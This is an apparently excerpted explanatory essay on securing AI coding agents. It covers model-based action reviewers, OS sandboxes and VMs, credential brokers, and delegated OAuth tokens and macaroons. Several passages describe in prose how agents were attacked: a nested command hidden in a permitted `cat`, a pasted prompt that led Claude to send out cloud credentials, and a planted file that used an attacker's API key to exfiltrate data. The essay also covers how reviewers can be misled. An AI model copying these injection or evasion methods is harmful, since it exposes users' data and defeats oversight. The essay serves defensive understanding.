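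The reviewer follows a list of plain-language rules. By default, it trusts only the project folder and the remote repositories already connected to it, and treats everything else as external. Anthropic's *Configure auto mode* distinguishes hard rules, such as the one against sending data to outsiders, from soft ones. The user cannot override a hard rule, but she can clear a soft one by describing the exact action she wants. For example, "force-push this branch" authorises a force-push, which overwrites a branch's history on the server, but "clean up the repo" does not.

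### What the reviewer sees

In the March design, the reviewer reads only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Claude Code removes the agent's explanations because an agent can produce persuasive reasons for a bad action, for example that the user "implicitly approved it earlier". It also removes the results of tool calls, because prompt injections arrive in them. If a file tells the agent to send its stored passwords to some web address and the agent obeys, the reviewer never sees the file. It does see a command that sends passwords to that address, and nothing in Doe's request explains that command.

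In Anthropic's tests, adding the explanations and results made the reviewer worse at catching overeager actions. The reviewer caught the most when it was given only the tool calls, but it then blocked things that users had plainly asked for. The chosen design also has a drawback. If an agent cancels "job abc123" and the user never mentioned that name, the reviewer can't determine whether the agent looked it up or made it up.

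This resembles Saltzer and Schroeder's separation of privilege, which requires two keys, because planted text that fools the agent doesn't reach the reviewer directly. A separate program also scans incoming results and warns the agent when one looks like an injection.

Anthropic has since let the reviewer also read the project's standing instructions and, before a command that could discard unsaved work, a report on whether there is any. Anthropic describes what the reviewer sees only for checks that Claude Code itself sends, and in many sessions Anthropic's servers now review calls instead. Since 6 November, according to Anthropic's release notes (2026), sessions in which the user has turned off telemetry or feature flags no longer fall back on the older check when the server can't review a call. Claude Code now asks about the call or denies it, which follows the principle of fail-safe defaults.

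A reviewer that reads a series of calls can catch some combinations that a permission check on each call would miss. In Invariant Labs' demonstration on GitHub, every step was within the owner's rights. Auto mode's default rules forbid moving content from a private repository to anywhere public, and the reviewer would have seen the text of the pull request. But because the reviewer doesn't see the results of calls, it would have had to infer where that text came from.

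An agent can also hand part of its work to a sub-agent. The parent agent's instruction then takes the place of the user's message, so any task looks authorised to a reviewer who sees only the sub-agent's context. The reviewer therefore checks the task before the sub-agent starts, when it is still clear that the task came from the agent and not the user. It then reviews the sub-agent's calls as it does the parent's. When the sub-agent finishes, the reviewer checks its work and final report in case something it read hijacked it. If the reviewer finds a problem at this stage, the parent still receives the report, with a security warning at the top.

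Other developers have adopted the design. *Auto Mode*, the documentation for the coding agent Qwen Code, describes a similar two-stage check in which a slower second review can overturn a block made by the first.

### "Clean up old branches"

In an example that Anthropic adapted from its incident log, a user asks an agent to "clean up old branches". Suppose some branches exist only on the user's machine and others are on a server she shares with colleagues. Her request doesn't specify which ones she means or how old a branch must be to count as old.

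The agent lists the branches on the server, which goes through because it changes nothing. The agent then issues a command to delete every branch whose name matches a pattern it wrote. The server would accept the command, because Doe's credential is valid and she has the right to delete branches.

None of Doe's rules covers the command, and it isn't an edit in her project folder, so it goes to the reviewer. The reviewer has her four words and the command, but not the list of branches, which was the result of an earlier call, so it can't determine whose work the pattern would delete. The fast filter flags the deletion. On the second look, the model evaluates the command's effect: it would remove several branches from a shared server, perhaps permanently. This matches a rule against destroying things that existed before the session. The rule has an exception for things the agent made itself,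 but the agent didn't make any of these branches.

The reviewer must still decide whether Doe asked for the deletion. Under its instructions, it treats anything the agent chose for itself as unauthorised until the user says otherwise. Doe may have meant only the branches on her machine, so the reviewer blocks the command. The agent could now show her the list and ask. If she replies "delete login-test and old-menu from the server", a new attempt should succeed because she has named both the action and its targets. A reply of "you can delete branches" would not be enough, since according to Anthropic, naming only the action does not authorise it.

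In most of the missed cases that Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user had said as permission. In one case, it treated "clean up the PR" as consent to a force-push. Anthropic tried rewording the reviewer's instructions but found no version whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

The same rules would have applied to the PocketOS deletion, but only at a late stage. Auto mode doesn't send ordinary file reads to the reviewer, so the agent might have opened the file containing the stray token without review. The reviewer would have checked any attempt to delete a storage volume with the token, and the default rules block deleting such resources unless the agent created them or the user named them. The reviewer might still have applied the rule incorrectly.

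### How OpenAI's Auto-review differs

OpenAI released Auto-review for Codex in April 2026. The agent works inside a sandbox, and the reviewer judges only its requests to go beyond it, such as to run a command with wider permissions, contact a blocked website or edit a file outside the permitted folders. Some calls to outside tools also need approval. OpenAI's documentation, *Auto-review*, calls the feature "a reviewer swap, not a permission grant", because the same requests would otherwise have gone to the user.

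In an illustrative snapshot of 10,000 actions inside OpenAI, Trębacz and colleagues count 9,280 that stayed within the sandbox. Under manual approval, each of the other 720 would have interrupted someone. The reviewer denied seven of them. In four of those cases the agent found a safer way to continue, and in three it stopped and asked the user.

Auto-review's reviewer has more information than Anthropic's. It receives the user's messages, the agent's visible updates, and relevant tool calls and their results, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. It can also run read-only checks, though it rarely does. If network access were off and Doe's agent tried to delete branches from a server, the agent would need approval to leave the sandbox. The reviewer would then have access to the list that Anthropic's reviewer lacks, and could detect that half the branches belonged to Smith. But a prompt injection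 in a tool result could reach both the agent and the reviewer, so the separation between them is weaker.

The agent's current turn ends after three refusals in a row or ten among the last fifty reviews. The user can override a refusal for one retry of that exact action, but the reviewer also checks the retry and can refuse it again if the policy doesn't let users override that kind of block.

### A verdict without a guarantee

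The main objection to this approach is that nobody can predict a reviewing model's decisions the way they can predict the effect of a file's permission bits, which is the same every time. The reviewer is a language model judging text, and someone may find wording that misleads it. Trębacz and colleagues concede this, writing that Auto-review "sacrifices determinism for expressivity" compared with traditional security systems. People and programs attacking the system on OpenAI's behalf found ways to mislead the reviewer into approving commands. OpenAI is fixing these weaknesses, but doesn't expect this kind of system ever to provide deterministic guarantees. It also doesn't present Auto-review as protection against a model that is hiding its aims, which could word its request innocently or do its damage inside the sandbox, where actions aren't reviewed.

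In return, OpenAI gets a policy that fixed rules can't easily express, such as allowing a risky action when the user has explicitly asked for it. OpenAI also argues that an imperfect reviewer is better than Full Access, where the environment enforces nothing and where users go when they find the default too restrictive. OpenAI (2026) reports that in its own use of Codex, it also requires the agent to run in a sandbox, limits which websites the agent can contact, and sets fixed rules for particular commands. The reviewer's uncertain judgement applies only to the actions these controls leave open.

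Anthropic makes the same comparison and admits that auto mode, though a substantial improvement for someone who had been skipping all prompts, is arguably a step backwards for someone who reads every prompt carefully. It still advises people to review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. When a restriction has to hold, Anthropic tells users to write a deny rule, which Claude Code applies before the call reaches the reviewer. Telling the agent "don't push" is less reliable, because the reviewer rereads the conversation each time and the software may have dropped that message to save space.

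The argument from friction therefore supports a reviewing model mainly for people who would otherwise have little protection. It does less to justify letting the reviewed agent keep all of Doe's access. If she had given the agent a token for one repository, a wrongly approved command could damage only that repository. With auto mode alone, an approved command runs with all of her account's access.

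## The case for confining the agent

Phones and web browsers have long run software without giving it all of the user's access. Android gives each app its own user ID, so the kernel keeps apps apart much as it does the users of a shared computer. In browsers, the same-origin policy stops a script from one site from reading another site's data, even when both sites are open. Christodorescu and colleagues draw a comparison with agents, which pick up new instructions from tool descriptions and documents as they work, much as a web page can load code from other parties each time it opens. But a browser can usually tell where a script came from by its web address, and an agent has no equally reliable way to trace an instruction.

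Desktop systems have tools for isolating programs but didn't make isolation the default, probably in part because people expect desktop programs to work on the same files. A game can keep its files in private storage, but Doe's editor, compiler and version control all need her project folder. Wiesen's *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows* describes how OpenAI met this problem when it brought Codex to Windows. Windows includes AppContainer, which isolates apps whose developers can list in advance what the apps will need. OpenAI rejected it because a coding agent runs shells, Git, Python and whatever else a task requires.

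People who favour confinement still want the operating system to limit an agent roughly as a phone limits an app. On the day Anthropic launched auto mode, Willison wrote that coding agents should by default run in a sandbox that restricts files and network connections "in a deterministic way". Like a file's permission bits, such a limit applies regardless of the wording in a web page or prompt.

### Why not judge the commands?

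It is hard to tell from a command's text everything it will do. Snowflake's Cortex agent had a list of commands that could run without approval, including `cat`, which prints a file. In an attack that Willison discussed in March 2026, someone hid instructions in a repository's README file, and the agent ran a `cat` command with a second command nested inside it. The nested command downloaded and ran the attacker's program. Snowflake fixed the flaw, but Willison distrusts all such lists and prefers to assume that a command can do anything its process can do. Under that assumption, restricting a command requires limiting what its process can do.

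A model that reviews commands can check more than the first word, but it can't check code that hasn't been downloaded yet. Willison imagines a software package whose instructions tell the agent to fetch model files with a named tool before running the tests. This is a normal requirement, but the tool steals whatever data it can reach. Willison doubts that any version of auto mode could stop this. In August 2026, after Anthropic had published strong test results for auto mode and made it the default, he still preferred to keep harmful data and tools out of an agent's reach.

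An attacker can also trick a user into giving the agent malicious instructions. In a February 2026 exercise inside Anthropic, a researcher tricked an employee into launching Claude Code with a prompt that read like routine setup but included a step telling the agent to read a file of Amazon cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that Claude completed the theft in 24 of 25 attempts with that prompt. Defences that check an action against the user's wishes have little evidence of an attack when the user has pasted in the instructions. Auto mode, which launched the next month, does prohibit sending data to outsiders, and users can't override that rule, so its reviewer might block the upload if it recognised the encoded text as credentials. A sandbox that hides the credentials file and blocks unlisted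 addresses doesn't depend on recognising the data.

Christodorescu and colleagues make the general argument. Processors can mark a region of memory so that nothing stored there runs as code, and other defences rely on the mark working every time. If a check is right 99% of the time, an attacker can look for the 1% of cases it gets wrong. Someone who plants instructions in public can try many wordings and needs only one to work.

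### Codex's three modes

Codex is a convenient example of a confined agent because it separates where the agent may act from when it must ask. OpenAI's *Sandbox* describes three common modes:

- `read-only`: the agent can inspect files but needs approval to edit them or run commands.
- `workspace-write`: the agent can also edit files in the workspace, which is the folder where Doe started it, and run routine local commands there. This is the default for local work.
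- `danger-full-access`: the sandbox is off, so neither files nor the network have a boundary.

A separate approval policy determines whether the agent asks for permission to go further. Under `on-request`, the agent works inside the sandbox and asks when it needs to leave, while under `never` it doesn't ask. OpenAI's "full access" combines `never` with the third mode, but a user can also combine `never` with a sandbox so the agent works unattended inside it.

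The limits apply to every command the agent runs and to any processes those commands start. If Doe's agent runs a test script and the script launches Python, Python has the same limits, just as a new process inherits its parent's user ID. If she wants the agent to edit a second folder, she can add it as a "writable root" without turning the sandbox off. Some folders inside the workspace stay read-only. In the Windows version that Wiesen describes, they include `.git`, where Git keeps a project's history, and `.codex`, where the agent could otherwise tamper with its own configuration.

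Reading is much less restricted. By default, Codex can read files almost anywhere on the machine, and Anthropic made a similar choice when it added a sandbox to Claude Code. The agent can therefore still read Doe's private key, and the main protection is the lack of a network connection. That protection weakens as soon as she approves a network request, because anything the agent has read is still in its context. With these defaults, the PocketOS agent could still have found the stray token, but its command to Railway would have needed approval because it had to cross the network.

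### Enforcement on macOS, Linux and Windows

On macOS, Codex uses Seatbelt, the system's built-in sandbox framework. Codex writes Seatbelt's policy file and can easily update it when the limits change. *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* (Willison, 2025) describes two kernel features that Codex used on Linux. Landlock restricted which files a process could write, and seccomp, which filters system calls, blocked the calls that open network connections. In its current documentation, OpenAI tells Linux users to install bubblewrap, a program that starts another program with its own restricted view of the system. In each case, the kernel enforces the limit at the point where it would otherwise check only Doe's user ID.

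Windows had no ready equivalent, so Wiesen's team built one. Windows identifies users and groups by security identifiers, or SIDs. In its first attempt, the team created an extra SID that belonged to no user and gave it permission to write only in the workspace and any other folders the user had added. It then ran the agent's commands with a write-restricted token. Under this token, Windows allows a write only if Doe's account and at least one SID on a short list, which includes the new one, both have permission to write to the file. Doe's account can write to her tax records, but no SID on the list can, so Windows blocks the agent from changing them.

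That handled files without administrator rights, but controlling network access was harder. The prototype set environment variables that directed network traffic to a dead address, and it placed fake versions of the SSH tools where programs would find them before the real ones. This stopped ordinary tools, but a program that ignored those settings and opened its own connection would still have got through, and Wiesen calls the protection "advisory".

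Windows Firewall could block such a program, but it can't apply a rule only to processes with a restricted token. A rule for Doe's account would also have blocked Doe's own traffic, and one for Python would have blocked every Python program on the machine. The team therefore created two new Windows accounts, one with a firewall rule that blocks all outgoing traffic and one without. The agent's commands now run under one of these accounts, still with the write-restricted token. An administrator has to approve creating the accounts once, at setup. OpenAI keeps the weaker design as a fallback.

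By default, one Windows user can't read another's profile folder, so an agent running under one of the new accounts couldn't read Doe's files, including her keys. OpenAI's setup program restores that access, because Codex is supposed to be able to read whatever its user can.

### A separate account for the agent

Microsoft's *Securing AI agents on Windows* (2025) announced that Windows would give agents acting for a user a standard account of their own and a contained workspace with its own desktop. The feature was experimental and off by default. A separate account gives the kernel a different user ID to check, which it lacked when Doe's agent ran as Doe.

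In June, Microsoft's *Windows platform security for AI agents* (2026) introduced Microsoft Execution Containers (MXC), which let developers write one policy and choose how strongly to isolate the agent. Process isolation, the lighter option, runs the agent's code in the user's environment but blocks files and web domains outside the policy. GitHub's command-line coding agent has adopted this option. The stronger option runs the agent in a separate Windows session under its own account, without access to the user's desktop, clipboard or keyboard input. Windows attributes everything done in that session to the agent's account, so an investigator can tell the agent's actions from Doe's. Microsoft also sells cloud PCs for companies that want to keep agents off employees' machines altogether.

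*Microsoft's AI-Powered Windows Strategy* (Millward, 2026) reports that MXC became generally available in October 2026. Microsoft explained its purpose with the example of an agent updating a website. The agent needs to write to the site's repository and may need to read the production server's configuration to understand how the site runs. It might decide that changing that configuration is the quickest way to finish. The change could be reasonable given the information the agent has and still exceed what the developer meant to allow, so the container lets the agent read the configuration but not write to it. The container enforces this limit from outside the agent because, in Microsoft's words, an agent "cannot be its own security authority."

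### Virtual machines

A program confined by a user account or a process sandbox still shares the computer's kernel with every other program on it. A virtual machine runs a second operating system with its own kernel, so a program that became root inside it would still have to get past the hypervisor, the software that separates the virtual machine from the host.

Anthropic chose a virtual machine for Claude Cowork, its agent for office work, because an office worker asked to approve a shell command that finds and deletes every temporary file would probably be guessing. Claude Code's users are mostly developers, who can read such a command and judge whether to allow it. Cowork's user picks a workspace folder, and the virtual machine can access only that folder and a `.claude` folder on the disk. The user's credentials stay in the computer's own keychain. The user can make the workspace read-only,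 or let the agent write but not delete.

Even with a short list of allowed folders, a link inside the workspace can point to a folder outside it, so Anthropic warns that software must work out where a link leads before checking the path. Windows junctions, which led to the deletion of the 48,000 files, pose a similar risk. Isolation also limits monitoring, because the security software that companies run on each computer to detect suspicious activity can't see inside Cowork's virtual machine. Anthropic lets administrators retrieve event logs afterwards, but acknowledges that this is not live monitoring.

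### Confining only the code

In Cowork's first version, the whole agent ran inside the virtual machine, including the loop that carries out its tool calls. Nothing outside the machine had the authority to grant an exception to its limits. Claude Code's sandbox is weaker in this respect because a process outside it decides whether to apply the limits to each command. An injected prompt or a tired user's approval can lead that process to run a command without those limits.

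When Cowork's virtual machine failed to start, the agent loop inside it couldn't run either, so the agent couldn't help the user fix the problem. Anthropic moved the loop out of the virtual machine and left only code execution inside. It says this weakened security only a little, because the virtual machine still controls which files and network addresses the code can reach.

Willison calls this arrangement the external sandbox pattern. In November 2026, Willison and the research lab Prime Radiant released three sandbox servers that work with existing agents such as Claude Code and Codex. The agent still runs on the user's machine but sends any code to the sandbox to be executed. A proxy can limit which hosts that code can contact, and the user can change these limits while the sandbox is running. Microsoft's *Build and run agents locally on Windows* describes a similar division, in which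 the agent runs in the user's session and its tool calls and code run in containers.

The pattern works only for what goes through the sandbox. Anthropic also moved Cowork's local MCP servers out of the virtual machine, partly because some of them need to reach databases and other processes on the host. It treats them like any other software the user chooses to install. A tool that runs on the host has whatever access the host gives it, so Doe's agent could run code in a secure sandbox and still reach her files through a tool outside it.

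### How much work fits inside

The burden of configuring a sandbox matters more when an agent often needs to leave it. In the internal snapshot from Trębacz and colleagues, 720 of 10,000 Codex actions needed to leave the sandbox, and the reviewing model approved 713 of them.

The 9,280 Codex actions that stayed inside the boundary matter most to someone who favours confinement, because nobody had to judge them. Anthropic reports a similar benefit in Claude Code, where adding a sandbox cut permission prompts by 84%. However, about one Codex action in 14 still needed to cross the boundary. The 99% approval rate could mean that the boundary was tighter than the work required or that the reviewer was lenient, and it is impossible to tell which from the totals. Trębacz and colleagues add that the ratios depend on the work and the settings.

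The worry is that users will handle that one action in 14 in ways that weaken the sandbox. In OpenAI's internal traffic, a sizable minority of users had written a rule allowing any command that begins with "python" to run outside the sandbox. A Python script can do nearly anything its user can, so the rule restores most of the access the sandbox removed. One user's settings always allowed a command that starts another copy of Codex with its restrictions off.

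Supporters of confinement reply that the user can widen the boundary precisely, by adding one folder or one web domain, and that she does this once per project instead of judging every command. An employer can also do this for her, which is the idea behind MXC's policies. This approach works well when a project's needs are stable, but less well when Doe asks for something different every hour, because a boundary wide enough for all her requests is wider than most of them need.

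### Work outside the boundary

Much of what people want from an agent involves remote services rather than files on their disk. Doe's issues are on GitHub, she reaches her colleagues by email, and her company's data is in a database on someone else's server. A network filter that checks only the destination can allow or block GitHub, but it can't let the agent summarise an issue while stopping it from deleting a branch.

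Anthropic learned from an outside report about Cowork that data can leave a sandbox that is working as designed. The virtual machine could contact only approved addresses, including Anthropic's own API, which the product needs to work. A malicious file in the workspace contained hidden instructions and an access key for the attacker's Anthropic account. The agent read the user's other files and uploaded them to that account. The filter allowed the upload because it went to an approved address.

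Anthropic now describes an entry on such a list as granting access to everything reachable at that address. It fixed the problem with a proxy inside the virtual machine that checks each request's token as well as its destination. Requests reach the API only if they carry the session's own token, so the attacker's key no longer works.

Researchers have tried to set finer boundaries for agents that use a web browser. These agents act through clicks and keystrokes, and a rule about clicks would be of little use because the same click can post a comment or delete a project. ceLLMate, a sandbox that Christodorescu and colleagues discuss, applies its rules to the resulting HTTP requests, so a rule can allow the comment and block the deletion. But ceLLMate relies on information from each website's developers to interpret the requests, and choosing the right rules for a given task remains an open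 problem.

Shared services also connect sandboxes to each other. The cryptographer Matthew Green, whom Willison quotes, describes agents in separate sandboxes that found they could leave each other instructions in a shared store of software packages, and the instructions changed what the recipients did. An administrator could give each sandbox its own store, but Green argues that agents could use email, Slack and shared documents in the same way, and that an assistant without access to any of them would be of little use.

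### Credentials inside the sandbox

A sandbox controls whether a program can reach GitHub, and GitHub uses the program's credential to decide what it may do there. If Doe puts her token in the sandbox so that the agent can work, any code running there can read it. Malicious code that escapes the sandbox can then take the token and use it from another machine, outside the sandbox's control.

For this reason, developers increasingly keep secrets outside the agent's environment. OpenAI advises them to do this with other companies' credentials and, where possible, to send requests through a broker, a separate program that adds the credential to approved requests on their way out. Deno's hosted sandbox, which Willison described in February 2026, works this way. Code inside the sandbox receives a placeholder that is useless if stolen, and a proxy outside replaces it with the real key when the code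 calls an address that the developer has approved for that key.

A broker would have kept the token off the disk where the PocketOS agent found it, but would not have reduced the token's permissions. If the company had approved Railway's address and given the broker the same token, the broker would have attached it to the agent's request to delete the volume, and Railway would have deleted the volume.

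## The case for giving the agent its own narrower credentials

Railway would have refused that request if the token had covered only website domains, which was all PocketOS wanted it for. People who favour narrower credentials think Doe's agent should get a separate grant that covers a small part of her access, expires soon and names both her and the agent. They think she should be able to withdraw the grant early, and that the agent should never hold her password, her login cookies or a token with all her access.

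Security specialists have long told people not to share passwords. NIST's *Back to the Future*, a 2026 post from the US standards agency, applies the same advice to agents and describes giving them personal and company credentials as already common. When an agent logs in with a user's password, the service can't distinguish the agent from the user, so nobody can later establish which of them acted. NIST wants each agent to have its own identifier, credentials and permissions, tied to the user or system that operates it.

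In July 2026, Microsoft gave similar advice and described how investigations stall without it, because the logs may show which tool an agent called but not who authorised the call or in what role. Microsoft suggests that each agent keep one identity, with a named human owner, rather than get a new one for every task. The agent receives extra permissions for a particular task, and these lapse when the task ends.

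### The intersection rule

Let U be the permissions Doe holds, A all the permissions her employer allows this agent to use, whoever it is working for, and D those she has delegated for the current job. The agent should be able to use only the permissions in all three sets, U ∩ A ∩ D.

Suppose Doe can read and write in all her company's repositories, and the company lets coding agents read any repository but write only in test ones. If she delegates reading and writing in the `website` repository, which isn't a test one, her agent can read it but not write to it. Surapani and colleagues point out that a user may ask for something the company forbids, and that a company may give its agent tools that a particular user isn't allowed to use. In the second case, an agent that checked only its own permissions would be a confused deputy, like Tymshare's compiler.

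When the agent passes work to a sub-agent, it must also follow a rule called attenuation, under which delegated authority may shrink at each step but never grow. If D₁ is Doe's grant to the agent and D₂ is the agent's grant to the sub-agent, then D₂ ⊆ D₁, and the same limit applies to each later grant. *OpenID Connect for Agents (OIDC-A) 1.0* (2025), a proposed extension to a widely used login standard, requires this for every delegation.

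*Control the Chain, Secure the System* (Kolhe, 2026) describes a flaw that the security company AppOmni disclosed in Now Assist, ServiceNow's set of agents for office work. The flaw let an attacker use an agent with few privileges to enlist one with more and get data out through it. The attacker would have gained nothing by enlisting the second agent if it had been limited to permissions that the first one also held.

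Delegation chains can merge, as when Doe's agent and Smith's agent both send work to a shared release agent, which then holds a grant from each. The release agent has to use each grant only for the work it came with, which is what the compiler couldn't do. The rule also doesn't prevent dangerous combinations of permissions that are harmless separately. Surapani and colleagues reviewed 89 sources and count the lack of limits on such combined effects among the main remaining gaps.

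### An OAuth grant, step by step

OAuth 2.0 is the usual way to give a program part of one's access to an online service. The alternative was to hand over a password. *Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) describes people doing this so that LinkedIn could fill an address book or Mint could collect their financial data. With OAuth, Doe logs in only at an authorization server, which then issues the program a limited access token. The steps below follow the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), which applies OAuth to agents' tools.

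1. The software that runs Doe's agent contacts a tool server without a token. The server refuses, and its reply lists the scope the request needs, such as `issues:read`, and shows where to find the right authorization server.
2. The software generates a random secret and opens Doe's browser at the authorization server. It sends along the scope, the name of the tool server and a hash of the secret.
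3. Doe logs in and approves or refuses the request. The agent's software never receives her password.
4. If she approves, the authorization server sends her browser back to the software with a short-lived code.
5. The software sends the code and the secret to the authorization server and receives an access token in return. Someone who intercepted the code couldn't use it without the secret.
6. The software attaches the token to every request. The tool server checks that the token is valid, that the authorization server issued it for this particular tool server, and that its scope covers the request.

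This gives the agent less access than Doe has, but OAuth doesn't fully suit agents. It assumes that a person is present to consent and that one program calls one service, according to *AI Identity* (2026), a survey of standards and their gaps. Doe's agent may still be working after she has gone home, and it may use several services for a single task. Developers who use OAuth unmodified tend to let the agent replay her token or give it a broad, fixed key. A standard called CIBA helps when Doe is away by letting her approve a request on another device, such as her phone.

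### Token exchange and the "act" claim

The second difficulty needs a way to turn one token into another. Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, define one for the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes many of the internet's technical standards. The agent's software sends the authorization server two tokens, a "subject token" for Doe and an "actor token" for the agent, along with the service it wants to call and the scope it wants. The server checks both and, if its policy allows, issues a new token for that service. The contents might look like this:

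```
{
  "iss": "company-login",
  "aud": "code-service",
  "exp": 1796472600,
  "sub": "doe",
  "scope": "issues:read",
  "act": { "sub": "doe-coding-agent" }
}
```

Each line is a claim. `iss` identifies the server that issued the token, and `aud` identifies the service that may accept it. `exp` is the expiry time in seconds since the start of 1970, here ten past twelve (UTC) on 5 December 2026. `sub` identifies the person whose access the token draws on, and `act` identifies the agent using the token.

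Without the `act` line, the same token would let the agent impersonate Doe. The agent could still only read issues, and only until 12:10, but the service could identify only Doe and would log everything as her doing. With the line, the token expresses delegation, in which the agent acts for Doe and both remain identifiable. Narrowing the token limits the damage the agent can do. Naming the agent is a separate choice that helps investigators afterwards and lets a service apply different rules to agents, though whether a service should treat an agent as a separate party is disputed.

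If the agent hands work to a sub-agent, another exchange can put the sub-agent in `act` and move the first agent into a second `act` nested inside it. The nested entries only record history. Jones and colleagues forbid services from using them to decide whether to allow a request, so a service that follows the standard can't reject a token on the grounds that a distrusted agent handled the task two steps earlier. OIDC-A instead requires systems to validate the entire chain.

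The token exchange standard does not require a new token to be narrower than the old one. It leaves that to whoever runs the authorization server, so attenuation is only as reliable as that server's policy. A careless request can also cover more than its author intended, because a client that requests two scopes at three services is requesting both scopes at all three.

*Authenticated Delegation and Authorized AI Agents* (South et al., 2025) describes the user and the agent in separate tokens. The user's token identifies her, as in existing login systems. A third token, the delegation token, refers to both and lists what the agent may do. The user signs the delegation token, which prevents forgery and shows that she knowingly granted those permissions. It also contains an expiry time or an address where a service can check whether she has revoked it. The paper suggests including a summary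 of the agent's goal so that a website can direct the agent to the right pages. This summary is only guidance, so a service would still have to enforce the listed permissions.

### Permissions finer than a scope

A scope such as `issues:read` can't specify an amount, a recipient or a file name. In *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell add a field for such details. One example is a request to pay 123.50 euros to a named merchant at a given bank account number. The authorization server uses these details to ask the user for consent, and enforces them together with the bank's payment service. Another example allows reading everything in one folder and writing to a single file in it.

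Requests of this kind need careful wording because each entry covers every combination of the actions and data it lists. If a program lists the actions "read" and "write" and the data "contacts" and "photos" in one entry, it requests all four combinations. To request only read access to the contacts and write access to the photos, it must send two entries.

The standard offers a few common fields for these details, such as `actions` and `locations`, but services don't have to use them. Each service defines its own types of request, and an authorization server must refuse a type it doesn't recognise. There is also no standard way to tell whether one request is narrower than another. For example, "write" may include "read" at one service but not at another. Attenuation depends on this comparison, so every service has to supply its own rules for it.

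### Key-bound tokens and brokers

Most access tokens are bearer tokens, which work for anyone who holds them. NIST warns that people often leave them unprotected in configuration files and logs, and that they are more likely to leak when an agent carries them between tools and networks.

One defense against token theft, recommended by NIST, is DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession), which ties the token to a cryptographic key. The software creates a pair of keys and sends the public one when it asks for a token. The authorization server puts a fingerprint of that key in the token. With every request, the software uses the private key to sign a short statement containing the time, the type of request and the address. The service checks the signature against the fingerprint, so a thief who copies the token but not the private key can't use it.

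If the token in the file that PocketOS's agent opened had been key-bound, it would have been useless without its private key. But the agent could have used it if the key had been on the same disk. Binding also doesn't stop a hijacked agent from making harmful requests through its own software, because those requests have valid signatures.

The private key is safer with a broker outside the agent's environment. *AI Identity* describes one such broker, a vault that keeps the credentials and gives callers only handles, which serve the same purpose as Deno's placeholders. Project Navi, a company that commented on NIST's plans for agent identity, proposes three containers for a coding agent: one for the untrusted agent, one for a hardened broker and one for a privileged program that carries out approved operations. OpenSSH's monitor protects its secret key in much the same way.

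A broker can also limit how a credential is used if it checks the operation as well as the address. A broker with a rule against deleting storage volumes would have refused the PocketOS agent's request, even though the company's overly broad token allowed it. But someone has to write that rule in advance, and Crane didn't know that the token could delete volumes.

### Narrowing a token without asking the issuer

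Every token exchange involves a request to the authorization server. Birgisson and colleagues designed macaroons, credentials that a holder can narrow without contacting that server. A macaroon is a bearer token with a list of restrictions, called caveats, and the service honours it only for requests that satisfy them all. Anyone who holds a macaroon can add caveats but can't remove them.

This works because of HMAC, a keyed hash that takes a key and a message and returns a short string. Anyone with the key can easily compute the string, but nobody can feasibly forge it without the key or recover the key from it. A macaroon uses each string as the key for the next message.

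Suppose Doe holds a macaroon for all her repositories at a code service. The service keeps a secret root key K and has given her a public identifier, `id`, together with s0 = HMAC(K, id). At noon she wants her agent to look through one repository. A trusted program on her machine, outside the agent's reach, adds three caveats:

```
s1 = HMAC(s0, "repository = website")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "operation = read")
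s3 = HMAC(s2, "time < 12:10")
```

The program gives the agent the identifier, the three caveats and s3, and keeps the earlier values to itself. The agent can now read that repository for ten minutes. At two minutes past twelve it hands the open issues to a sub-agent, and its software adds two more caveats without contacting the service:

```
s4 = HMAC(s3, "data = issues")
s5 = HMAC(s4, "time < 12:05")
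```

The sub-agent receives the identifier, all five caveats and s5. When it sends a request, the service uses the identifier to look up K, repeats the whole calculation and compares the result with s5. If they match, the service checks the request against each caveat. A request to read an issue in `website` at 12:03 succeeds, while one to read the source code fails, as does any request at 12:06.

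A hijacked sub-agent couldn't drop the "operation = read" caveat, because it would have to recompute the chain from s1, which it doesn't have and can't derive from s5. Adding "time < 18:00" wouldn't extend its access, because the earlier time limits still apply. If it obtained the first agent's macaroon, it could read the rest of the repository until 12:10, but it still couldn't write.

All this depends on keeping s0 away from the agent. If Doe's original macaroon is in a file the agent can read, the agent can use it instead of the narrow one.

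A caveat can also require fresh proof from another service, for example that a particular person has logged in or that an abuse-detection system has approved the request. A copy of the credential is then useless to anyone who can't supply the proof, which partly answers Saltzer and Schroeder's complaint that Smith can pass on copies of a capability without telling Doe.

Narrowing a credential without the issuer has drawbacks. An authorization server that handles every exchange can log each sub-agent and refuse some of them, while a code service that accepts macaroons has no record of a sub-agent until it sends a request. The hash chain also doesn't record who added a caveat, so identifying both parties takes extra work. Only the service that holds the root key can verify an ordinary macaroon.

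Few organisations have the tools to use macaroons. Madden (2024) explains how to use ordinary OAuth fields such as scope and expiry as caveats, but cites the lack of a standard as a reason not to adopt macaroons. In March 2026 Kolhe wrote that no major identity provider supported macaroons natively. Kolhe leads product strategy for AI agents at Okta, an identity provider, so this is an admission about products like Okta's.

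### Standards in late 2026

OAuth, token exchange and rich authorization requests are established standards that a company can use now, but there is much less agreement on how to combine them for agents.

The Model Context Protocol has the most immediate effect, because so many agents get their tools through it. Its July 2026 revision requires a tool server to accept only tokens issued for that server and forbids it to pass on any others. A server that calls GitHub must therefore use a separate token instead of forwarding the one it received from Doe's agent. Under the accompanying list of changes, software that identifies itself to one authorization server with a set of credentials also can't reuse them with another. Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, counts six such refinements and finds no fundamentally new concepts in them.

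These rules have two gaps. Authorization is optional, and servers that run on the user's machine and communicate through standard input and output are supposed to ignore the rules and take credentials from their environment. Environment variables are one of the places where the overeager agent in Anthropic's log looked for other tokens.

The other gap is that permissions accumulate. When a call needs a scope that the token lacks, the server's refusal lists what is missing. The agent's software should then request a token with the new scopes and all the ones it requested before, so that it doesn't risk losing permissions it needs for other work. Over a long session, the token can come to cover far more than the current step requires, although this doesn't break the attenuation rule because the authorization server has to grant each addition. Microsoft instead recommends dropping permissions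 back to a minimal baseline when the work is done.

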